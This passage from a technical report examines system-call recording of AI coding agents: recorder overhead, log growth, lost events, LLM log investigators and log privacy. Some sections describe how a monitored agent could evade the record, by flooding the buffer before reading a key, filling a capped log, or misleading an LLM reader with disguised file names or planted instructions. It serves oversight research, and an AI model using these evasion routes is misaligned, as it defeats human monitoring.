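For strace, the number of recorded calls has to include those that it leaves out of the log, unless the operator uses `--seccomp-bpf`.

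The formula also doesn't account for parallel work. A build may run eight compilers at once on eight processor cores. With eBPF, each core does its own share of the recording, so 20 seconds of extra work might lengthen the build by only 2.5 seconds. A single strace process can't spread the work across cores because it handles the stops of all eight compilers one at a time, and a compiler may have to wait while strace handles another's stop.

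A small slowdown over a whole session can hide a large one in a single command. If recording lengthens a 60-second build to 80 seconds, and the agent runs that build once in a 10-minute session, the session takes only about 3% longer. But if the harness stops any command after 70 seconds, the build now fails. The agent receives an error caused by the recorder's delay and may change its approach. The log would still be accurate, but recording would have helped cause the behaviour it shows.

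### strace in the ACE sessions

King and colleagues ran strace on real agents in all 4,047 sessions of their ACE dataset. The median session lasted 8.8 seconds and the mean was 14.9 seconds. The researchers give no matching times without strace, so these figures don't show how much it slowed the agents.

At the model's assumed 10 microseconds per log entry, the average of about 3,500 entries per session would add roughly 0.035 seconds, or 0.2% of the mean session. This estimate is too low because strace ran without `--seccomp-bpf`, so it also slowed calls it did not log. If the programs made ten times as many calls as the log contains, strace would have added 0.35 seconds, or a little over 2%.

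In the busiest 1% of malicious sessions, the agent's programs made far more calls than this, with at least 235,186 to `openat` alone, which would add 2.4 seconds at the same assumed delay per call. That is small compared with the 180-second time limit, and nine sessions in ten finished within 22.4 seconds. For such short sessions, strace was probably a reasonable choice even if the true delay per call was several times the assumed value.

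In the experiments with Tether, however, strace was slow enough to be a drawback.

### Two tests with Claude Code

Zheng and colleagues timed Claude Code, using a Claude 4 model, on three common programming jobs, running each job three times with AgentSight and three times without it. With AgentSight, the average time rose from 127.98 to 132.33 seconds for examining and summarising a repository, from 22.54 to 23.64 seconds for writing a short monitoring script, and from 92.40 to 92.72 seconds for compiling a whole repository with several compilers running in parallel.

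These are increases of 3.4%, 4.9% and 0.4%, an average of 2.9%. The researchers say in their abstract that AgentSight adds less than 3%, which is true of the average but not of two of the three jobs.

Bao and colleagues tested AgentLoupe on a similar set of jobs, using a newer version of Claude Code, a different repository and a machine with four processor cores. They ran each job five times in each of four conditions: with no recorder, with AgentSight, with AgentLoupe, and with a version of AgentLoupe that did not pass labels between processes and files. The table shows the increase in average running time in both studies.

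| Job | AgentSight, original test | AgentSight, later test | AgentLoupe without label passing | AgentLoupe |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Summarising a repository | 3.4% | 4.5% | 1.7% | 4.5% |
| Writing a script | 4.9% | 2.5% | 3.1% | 8.0% |
| Compiling | 0.4% | 1.7% | −0.1% | 7.7% |

AgentSight caused a modest slowdown in both tests, but the job it slowed most was different in each. The tests used different machines, repositories and software versions, any of which might explain this. It could also be due to chance, as neither paper reports how much the individual runs varied.

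The compilation results are also hard to explain with the cost model alone. In the original test, AgentSight added 4.35 seconds to the summary and only 0.32 seconds to the compilation. One would expect the opposite, because a compiler opens many files while an agent writing a summary mostly waits for replies. AgentSight doesn't record ordinary reads and writes, so a compilation produces fewer recorded calls, and it has to process more model traffic during the summary. But the simplest explanation may be that the model took slightly longer to reply in some runs than in others.

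AgentLoupe's figures for compilation are more informative because compiling involves few exchanges with the model. Compilation took 23.00 seconds without a recorder, 22.97 seconds with label passing turned off and 24.78 seconds with the full system. This suggests that most of AgentLoupe's slowdown comes from updating labels as processes start and pass files to each other.

Label passing added 1.8 seconds to the compilation and almost 5 seconds to each of the other jobs. In seconds, then, Bao and colleagues are correct that its overhead is lowest for compilation. As a share of the running time, the overhead was highest for compilation, at about 8%. For long builds, that percentage is a better guide to AgentLoupe's overhead than the 1.8 seconds.

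### Agent-Warden's synthetic load

In their timing test, Cui and colleagues replaced the model with a program that imitates an agent's activity. The program starts a process, runs a command, reads and writes a file, and renames it, repeating this cycle 1,000 times. They timed it over 90 rounds, with and without Agent-Warden, on an ordinary x86-64 computer and a slower ARM64 machine.

| Machine | How Agent-Warden stores marks | Increase in running time | Extra system processor time |
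|---|---|---|---|
| x86-64 | By process number | 0.2% ± 1.2 | 0.6% ± 3.1 |
| x86-64 | With the kernel's own records | 1.1% ± 1.4 | 2.5% ± 3.3 |
| ARM64 | By process number | 3.5% ± 0.4 | 3.7% ± 0.8 |
| ARM64 | With the kernel's own records | 3.5% ± 0.4 | 3.7% ± 0.8 |

The numbers after the ± signs are standard deviations, which show how much individual rounds varied. If the rounds were independent, averaging 90 of them would reduce the uncertainty in the first result to about 1.2 divided by the square root of 90, or 0.13 percentage points. The 0.2% increase could therefore be close to zero, but the 3.5% increase on ARM64 is almost certainly real.

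These results also allow a rough check of the assumed delay per call. Without Agent-Warden, the program took 1.57 seconds on x86-64 and 8.30 seconds on ARM64. If those times cover all 1,000 cycles, as seems likely, Agent-Warden added between 3 and 17 microseconds per cycle on x86-64 and about 290 on ARM64.

The researchers do not say how many calls a cycle contains. If ten calls in each cycle triggered the recorder, recording would add between 0.3 and 1.7 microseconds per call on x86-64 and about 29 on ARM64. The true number of calls could be quite different, but the delay per call would still be many times longer on ARM64. Measurements from a fast server may therefore greatly underestimate the delay on a small device.

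Starting a process is slow, so Agent-Warden's recording takes up only a small share of each cycle. That share could be much higher for a program that mostly makes thousands of tiny reads, because each read takes far less time than starting a process.

### AgentSpy and the variation between runs

Bühler and colleagues ran the most careful of the tests with real agents. For each of the three models in their reliability study, they chose the fastest task, the slowest and one from the middle. They measured the slowdown from the audit system, LAUREL and Zeek on these nine combinations of model and task, and the slowdown from Falco on three more from their security study. They ran each combination ten times with recording and ten times without, for 240 runs in total.

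They then compared the two sets of times for each combination with a Mann-Whitney test, which ranks all 20 times and checks whether one set tends to rank higher. None of the 12 differences was significant at the usual 5% threshold. The smallest p-value was 0.16, so if recording had no effect, a difference at least that large would appear in about 16% of such experiments.

In eight of the 12 comparisons, the median run was faster with recording than without it. In one of these, an average-length task with DeepSeek V4 Flash, the median fell from 265.3 to 185.0 seconds. Recording can't speed an agent up by 80 seconds, so the difference must come from variation between runs. The model may take a longer route to the answer in one run than in another, or its provider may respond more slowly.

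The same variation can hide a real slowdown. With Falco running, the median time for one security task rose 32%, from 107.1 to 141.2 seconds. This was one of the comparisons with a p-value of 0.16, so chance could easily explain the increase, but the test doesn't rule out that Falco caused part of it.

Bühler and colleagues conclude that any overhead is small compared with the variation between runs and is unlikely to matter in practice. That is reasonable for someone waiting for an agent to finish a task, who would not notice a few extra seconds when the next run might take a minute longer. It is less convincing for an operator who runs thousands of sessions and pays for the machines, because a constant 5% overhead would still increase the bill.

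The times also cover only the command that runs the agent. They exclude starting the recorders and collecting the logs, which could noticeably lengthen a session of only a few seconds.

### How many runs a reliable test needs

The standard deviation in AgentSpy's runs ranged from 7% to 85% of the median time. A common rule of thumb gives the number of runs needed to have an 80% chance of detecting a difference at the usual 5% threshold:

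```
runs with recording  =  16 x (standard deviation / difference)^2
```

The test requires equal numbers of runs with and without recording. To detect a 3% slowdown when the standard deviation is 20%, a researcher would need about 700 runs of each kind. Even with a standard deviation of 7%, the lowest in AgentSpy's test, the researcher would need 87 of each.

Bühler and colleagues similarly calculated that they would have needed 30 runs with recording and 30 without to detect the largest difference they observed, and 18,200 of each to detect the smallest. Their 240 runs took 20 hours of agent time, an average of five minutes each. At that rate, the larger experiment would take more than four months for a single combination of model and task.

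AgentSight's three runs and AgentLoupe's five look few by comparison. If their times varied by only 7%, the average of three runs with recording would typically differ from the average of three without it by about 6%, even if the recorder didn't slow the agent at all. For five runs, the typical difference would be about 4%. Most of the percentages in the two studies are no larger than this. The studies are good evidence that neither recorder makes an agent several times slower, but they have too few runs to distinguish a 1% slowdown from a 5% one.

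### Estimating the cost for other work

These percentages don't apply to strace, which stops the program at each system call. None of the four systems does this, so they probably add much less time per call than strace does. A session that they slow by 3% could slow far more under strace if its commands make many calls.

The percentages are also a poor guide to the slowdown for commands that make many calls in a short time, such as installing thousands of small files or searching a large directory. Most of the timed jobs included long waits for a model, which reduce any recorder's share of the total time. AgentSpy's audit rules also left out ordinary reads and writes. An operator who added rules for these calls would record far more events and might fill the audit queue.

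A better way to measure the slowdown is to replay an agent's commands without the model. An operator can take the commands from a recorded session and run them many times in two identical containers, with the recorder on in only one. Alternating between the containers means that changes in the machine's other work affect both about equally. Dividing the extra time by the number of system calls gives a measured delay per call to replace the assumed 10 microseconds.

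Replay works best for builds, tests and file operations, because they behave much the same each time. Commands that use the internet need stored replies, or the network will add variation between runs, as the model did. Replay also can't show whether a slower command would have changed what the agent did, so the operator should check separately whether any command comes close to the harness's time limit.

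## How large do the logs grow, and can anyone read them?

Sessions in the ACE dataset averaged about 3,500 log entries. If an entry takes 200 bytes, a session takes 0.7 MB and 30,000 sessions take 21 GB, which fits on a cheap USB stick, so storage is seldom the obstacle. But those 30,000 sessions contain 105 million entries, and a person reading one per second without a break would need more than three years to read them all.

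### What makes a log grow

The average already includes `read` and `write`, which are among the 15 calls King and colleagues recorded. These two calls can outnumber all the others when a program handles a large file. Copying a 1 GB file in 128 KB pieces takes about 8,000 reads and 8,000 writes, which add 3.2 MB to the log. A recorder that logs only file opens would write two entries for the same copy.

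The log also grows with the amount of data it keeps from each call. strace prints unusual bytes as codes of up to four characters, so the 256 bytes that King and colleagues kept of each string can take about 1,000 characters. If every entry were that long, 30,000 sessions would need about 115 GB. With no limit on string length, the log would contain every copied file twice, once from the reads and once from the writes.

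A few extreme sessions can account for much of the total. The busiest 1% of ACE's malicious sessions (about 13) each made at least 235,186 `openat` calls. If the average of 3,500 covers the whole dataset, these calls make up at least a fifth of its 14 million entries. A session with that many calls would write 47 MB, so an operator should plan for the worst session as well as the average one. Cutting the log off at a fixed size would be risky, because an agent could fill it with harmless calls and then act without being recorded. Stopping the session when the log reaches the limit would be safer.

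### Leaving events out

Recording fewer kinds of call is the simplest way to shrink a log, but every omission makes some later question harder to answer. ACE's list, for example, has no calls that rename files. If a Python script renamed a stolen key file to something harmless-looking and another program later uploaded it, the log would contain both names but no record that they belonged to the same file.

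To keep AgentSpy's logs to a manageable size, Bühler and colleagues dropped most calls on files that were already open, but they don't report how much space this saved. The main information lost is how much data a program read or wrote. For network connections, a monitor such as Zeek can supply the missing byte counts.

Filtering by process tree saves the most space on a busy host, where most calls have nothing to do with the agent. It saves nothing if each container already has its own strace. The filter also removes the record of work that other programs do for the agent. An operator could reduce this loss by keeping the whole host's log for a week and only the agent's calls for longer.

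### Merging without losing the cause

An operator can also shrink a log by merging repeated events, as AgentSpy and AgentSight do. But merging can hide the order of events, which matters when an investigator wants to trace a cause. Suppose that a log contains these three events:

```
10:01  report.py reads   notes.txt
10:02  the agent writes  notes.txt
10:03  report.py reads   notes.txt
```

If the recorder merges the two reads into one at 10:01, the log no longer has a path from the agent to `report.py`. The recorder can safely drop the second read only if nothing has written to the file since the first. It can likewise drop a process's second write to a file if the process has received no new data since its first. Under these two rules, the log keeps every path by which one program could have influenced another, but loses the number of events, their sizes and some of their times.

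In *Benchmarking and Exploring the Capabilities of LLMs for Attack Investigations*, Anand, Kantchelian and colleagues (2026) used SPADE, which converts raw logs into provenance graphs, and wrote each edge of the graph on one line. For their 18 Linux scenarios, this reduced 74,800 lines from the audit system to about 18,000. Part of this reduction loses no information, because the audit system spreads each call over several lines. The Windows logs, from a more verbose recorder, shrank by factors of about 170 to 560. The researchers did not test whether the reduction preserved every causal link.

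### Reducing a trace to a fingerprint

*Preflight* (Jandali, Sheybani and colleagues, 2026) describes a system that reduces traces much further. The system checks third-party Python packages before a program uses them. It installs a package in a restricted container, calls the functions the program needs, and records both steps with strace. It then reduces the traces and some other records to a fingerprint, which lists the network addresses the package contacted, the programs it started, the lasting changes it made to files, the sensitive environment variables it read, and the categories of system call it used.

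The fingerprint leaves out process numbers, temporary paths and routine installer activity, all of which change from run to run. This makes it easy to compare two versions of a package:

```
new behaviour = fingerprint(new version) - fingerprint(old version)
```

The minus sign removes everything that also appears in the old version. For a compromised release of Ultralytics, an image-recognition package, the comparison left three new network addresses and three paths to the program `curl`. Preflight classified the release as malicious and all 100 harmless packages in the test as clean.

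The fingerprint can mislead when there is no earlier version to subtract. Preflight classified a release of another package, DurableTask, as malicious because of three network addresses, but two of them belonged to the test container. The fingerprint also does not fully separate what happened during installation from what happened when the program called a function. Jandali and colleagues keep the raw traces so that someone can check such cases.

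An operator could make a similar fingerprint for each agent session and read the raw log only when the fingerprint contained something unexpected. But agents do different work in each session, so there is no obvious "old version" to subtract. Repeated runs of the same task would probably be the closest substitute.

### How to tell that events are missing

A recorder in the kernel can lose events the operator meant to keep if its buffer fills. Suppose an 8 MB buffer holds 40,000 events and the collector can remove 20,000 per second. If a command produces 100,000 events per second, the buffer fills in half a second. The recorder then loses four of every five events until the command slows down.

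These losses happen when the machine is busiest, and an agent could cause them deliberately by starting a program that makes many system calls just before it reads a private key. An attack that exhausts the machine's resources could have the same effect. strace avoids this problem by making the traced program wait, although its log can still fill the disk.

A good recorder counts the events it loses. The operator should save this count at regular intervals, because a total at the end of the session might show that 500 events are missing but not when the recorder lost them. A recorder can locate a gap more precisely if it numbers every event before placing it in the buffer. If event 8,902 follows event 8,841 in the log, the 60 events between them are missing.

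Even without numbers, a log may contain signs of a gap, such as an exit by a process with no recorded start, or a write to descriptor 7 when no earlier call returned 7. These signs are weaker evidence, since the process might have been running before the recorder started. The harness could also run a small command with a unique tag every minute. If a tag is missing, the recorder was not working properly at that time. Even if every tag is present, there may be short gaps between them.

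### Reading by hand

Hugging Face recovered about 17,600 actions after the July intrusion. Help Net Security calculates that a person who read one action per minute would need twelve days without sleep to read them all. Working eight-hour days, the same person would need more than seven weeks. A system-call log of the same activity would have been far longer.

An investigator usually searches a log rather than reading it from beginning to end. To find out whether an agent opened a particular key, they can search for the key's file name, which takes seconds even in a 21 GB log. They then read the lines around each match and follow the process numbers back to the command.

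Searching works only for someone who knows what to look for. The AgentSpy rules that missed the malicious Git remote had the same limitation. There is no obvious search term for finding out whether the agent did anything it should not have done, and researchers have begun to use language models to answer that question.

### Language models as log readers

Anand and colleagues built a benchmark, AuditBench, to measure how well models investigate attacks in audit logs. It has 51 scenarios from Linux and Windows machines. The researchers recorded 25 in their own virtual machines and took 26 from OpTC, a large public collection of system logs. None involves an AI agent, but the logs contain the same kinds of process, file and network events as an agent's logs would.

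The models had four tasks: to decide whether an alert was a real attack, find changes that would let an attacker return later, find connections that could give an attacker control of another machine, and find stolen data. The logs were too long to give to a model at once, so the researchers cut them into chunks of 1,000 raw lines or 400 lines of graph edges. Each chunk was 100,000 to 128,000 tokens, the pieces of text a model processes. At 1,000 lines per chunk, an average ACE session would fill three and a half chunks.

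The table shows the results for the first task, using graph edges.

| Model | Attacks recognised, own recordings | Harmless chunks flagged | Attacks recognised, OpTC | Harmless chunks flagged |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5 | 5 of 5 | 3 of 21 | 5 of 5 | 12 of 145 |
| GPT-5 mini | 2 of 5 | 0 of 21 | 5 of 5 | 12 of 145 |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 5 of 5 | 18 of 21 | 5 of 5 | 116 of 145 |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 5 of 5 | 18 of 21 | 5 of 5 | 115 of 145 |
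| Llama 4 Maverick | 5 of 5 | 0 of 21 | 5 of 5 | 24 of 145 |

The perfect scores on OpTC are less impressive than they look. A model received credit for an attack if it flagged any chunk of that scenario, and each attack had at least three chunks. A model that flagged 80% of all chunks at random would have about a 99% chance of getting credit for all five attacks. The two Gemini models flagged about that share of the harmless chunks, so their scores are almost no evidence that they understood the logs.

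The models did best at finding data theft, which is also something an auditor would likely check for in an agent's logs. GPT-5 found all seven thefts and raised three false alarms. Connections to other machines were much harder to find. On OpTC, the best model found 7 of 19 and raised 30 false alarms. All five models date from 2025, so current ones may well do better.

Nineteen of the false alarms were each raised by at least four of the five models, and in 18 of these the models relied heavily on the names of files, programs or scheduled tasks. For example, one harmless task seemed suspicious because it was named `clear_logs`. An agent chooses the names of the scripts it writes, so it could probably make a harmful script look routine to a model reading the log. It could also put instructions to that model into a file name or a command. Anand and colleagues did not test attacks meant to deceive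 the models.

Most other false alarms came from only one or two models, so an operator could reduce them by running several models and acting only when most of them flag an attack. This would cost more and might miss attacks that only one model detects.

Models also misread logs because they lack information about what is normal on a particular machine. *Know the Normal, Track the Attack* (Zheng, He and colleagues, 2026) examines published reports from an earlier system, OCR-APT. The reports described routine monitoring programs such as `vmstat` and `lsof` as reconnaissance by an attacker. On one dataset, OCR-APT's report placed only 3 of 16 known signs of the attack in the correct stage. The paper's system, ANCHOR, gives the model a description of normal activity on the machine and a running record of well-supported findings. This approach should work better for a server with a steady routine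 than for an agent whose tasks vary.

### Narrowing the search before reading

*MINOS*, a newer system, doesn't give a model the whole log. Wang, Li and colleagues (2026), in *MINOS*, store the events as a provenance graph in a database and start from one event that is already known to be suspicious. The system then works backwards in a loop:

1. A planning model proposes what the attacker probably did just before, and describes the events that would confirm it.
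2. A second model turns the description into a database query. It first asks only how many events match. If there are more than 50, the planner has to narrow the request, for instance to a shorter period.
3. One model argues that a matching event belongs to the attack and another argues that it is harmless. A third decides between them.
4. If the event belongs to the attack, a further model adds it to a summary that guides the next round.

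Counting events first keeps the system from fetching every event connected to a busy process such as a shell, which may have thousands. When Wang and colleagues turned this step off, the average investigation used 248,000 tokens instead of 164,000, and the results included more unrelated events.

The system was tested on 14 attacks. Recall is the share of attack events that a system finds, and precision is the share of the events it reports that belong to the attack.

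| System | Recall | Precision | Events in the result (true number: 24) |
|---|---|---|---|
| NoDoze, based on how rare events are | 0.72 | 0.14 | 129 |
| DepImpact, based on scores passed along the graph | 0.66 | 0.24 | 68 |
| One model with the same tools | 0.40 | 0.15 | 120 |
| MINOS | 0.92 | 0.64 | 35 |

A person could check 35 events in an afternoon. On average, about 22 of them belong to the attack and 13 do not, while two attack events are missing. An investigation took about 21 minutes, much slower than the two older methods, which needed a few seconds, but much faster than reading the logs by hand.

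The test made the task easier than it would be in practice. The system always started from the last malicious event of a real attack, so it never had to determine whether there had been an attack. An auditor could get a starting point from one of AgentSpy's rules, but a false alert would make the system search for the causes of a harmless event. Most of the attacks also come from datasets that have been public for years, so the models' training data may include descriptions of the attacks.

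### Passwords and personal data in the log

A detailed log can be a better target for a thief than the machine it describes. In an example from King and colleagues, a program reads an Amazon credentials file, and the log entry includes the beginning of the file. The first 28 bytes in the format they show are a heading and a label, so strace's default limit of 32 bytes would keep only four characters of the access key's identifier. Their limit of 256 bytes would keep both the identifier and the secret key. ACE used fake credentials, but an ordinary agent would use real ones.

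Command lines can also expose secrets. If an agent passes an access token to `curl` as an argument, the token enters the log even if the recorder ignores all reads and writes. Sending the log to another machine protects it from the agent but creates another copy of the token. Anyone who can read the log can use the token until the operator replaces it.

The recorder can remove secrets before it writes an entry. For example, halo-record searches for common formats of secrets and personal data, according to Help Net Security. This works for access keys with a fixed prefix and length, but it can miss an ordinary password that looks like any other word. Replacing values with hashes is safer for long random keys than for personal data such as phone numbers, which are few enough that someone could hash every possible number and look for a match.

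For most audits, it is probably better not to record file contents by default. An investigator could still see from the log that a program opened the credentials file and contacted an outside host, but could not confirm what the program sent. Encryption often prevents that even when contents are recorded.

Using a commercial language model to read the log adds another risk, because the operator sends the log to the model's provider. Wang and colleagues acknowledge this privacy problem and propose running smaller models locally. In their tests, however, replacing the main reasoning model with a smaller open one cut precision from 0.64 to 0.33.

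### How long to keep the log

The EU AI Act requires operators of high-risk systems to keep logs. These systems include AI that screens job applicants or assesses whether someone should get a loan, but would not normally include a coding agent.

Article 12 of the Act requires a high-risk system to be able to record events automatically throughout its lifetime. The records must help people identify risks and monitor how the system works in use. Under Articles 19 and 26, the provider and the organisation using the system must each keep the logs they control for a period that suits the system's purpose. The minimum is six months, unless another law, particularly one on data protection, provides otherwise.

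A 2026 amendment postponed these duties to 2 December 2027 for uses that the Act lists as high-risk, such as hiring, and to 2 August 2028 for AI in regulated products, such as medical devices. The National Law Review reported in July 2026, in *EU Digital Omnibus on AI Enters Into Force*, that the amendment had taken effect.

The Act does not specifically require system-call logs, and it leaves the method of recording open. For a hiring agent, a system-call log might show that the agent opened an applicant's CV, but not why it ranked that applicant last. A record of the agent's inputs and decisions would probably serve Article 12's purpose better. A system-call log would be a useful supplement if someone suspects that the agent also opened files it had no reason to use.

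Under the earlier assumptions, 30,000 sessions a month would produce 126 GB of logs in six months, so storage cost is a poor reason to delete them early. The personal data they contain is a better reason. Where no law requires the full log, an operator could delete the raw entries after a few weeks and keep a reduced graph of programs, files and hosts for longer. The graph would contain fewer secrets, but its file names could still identify people.
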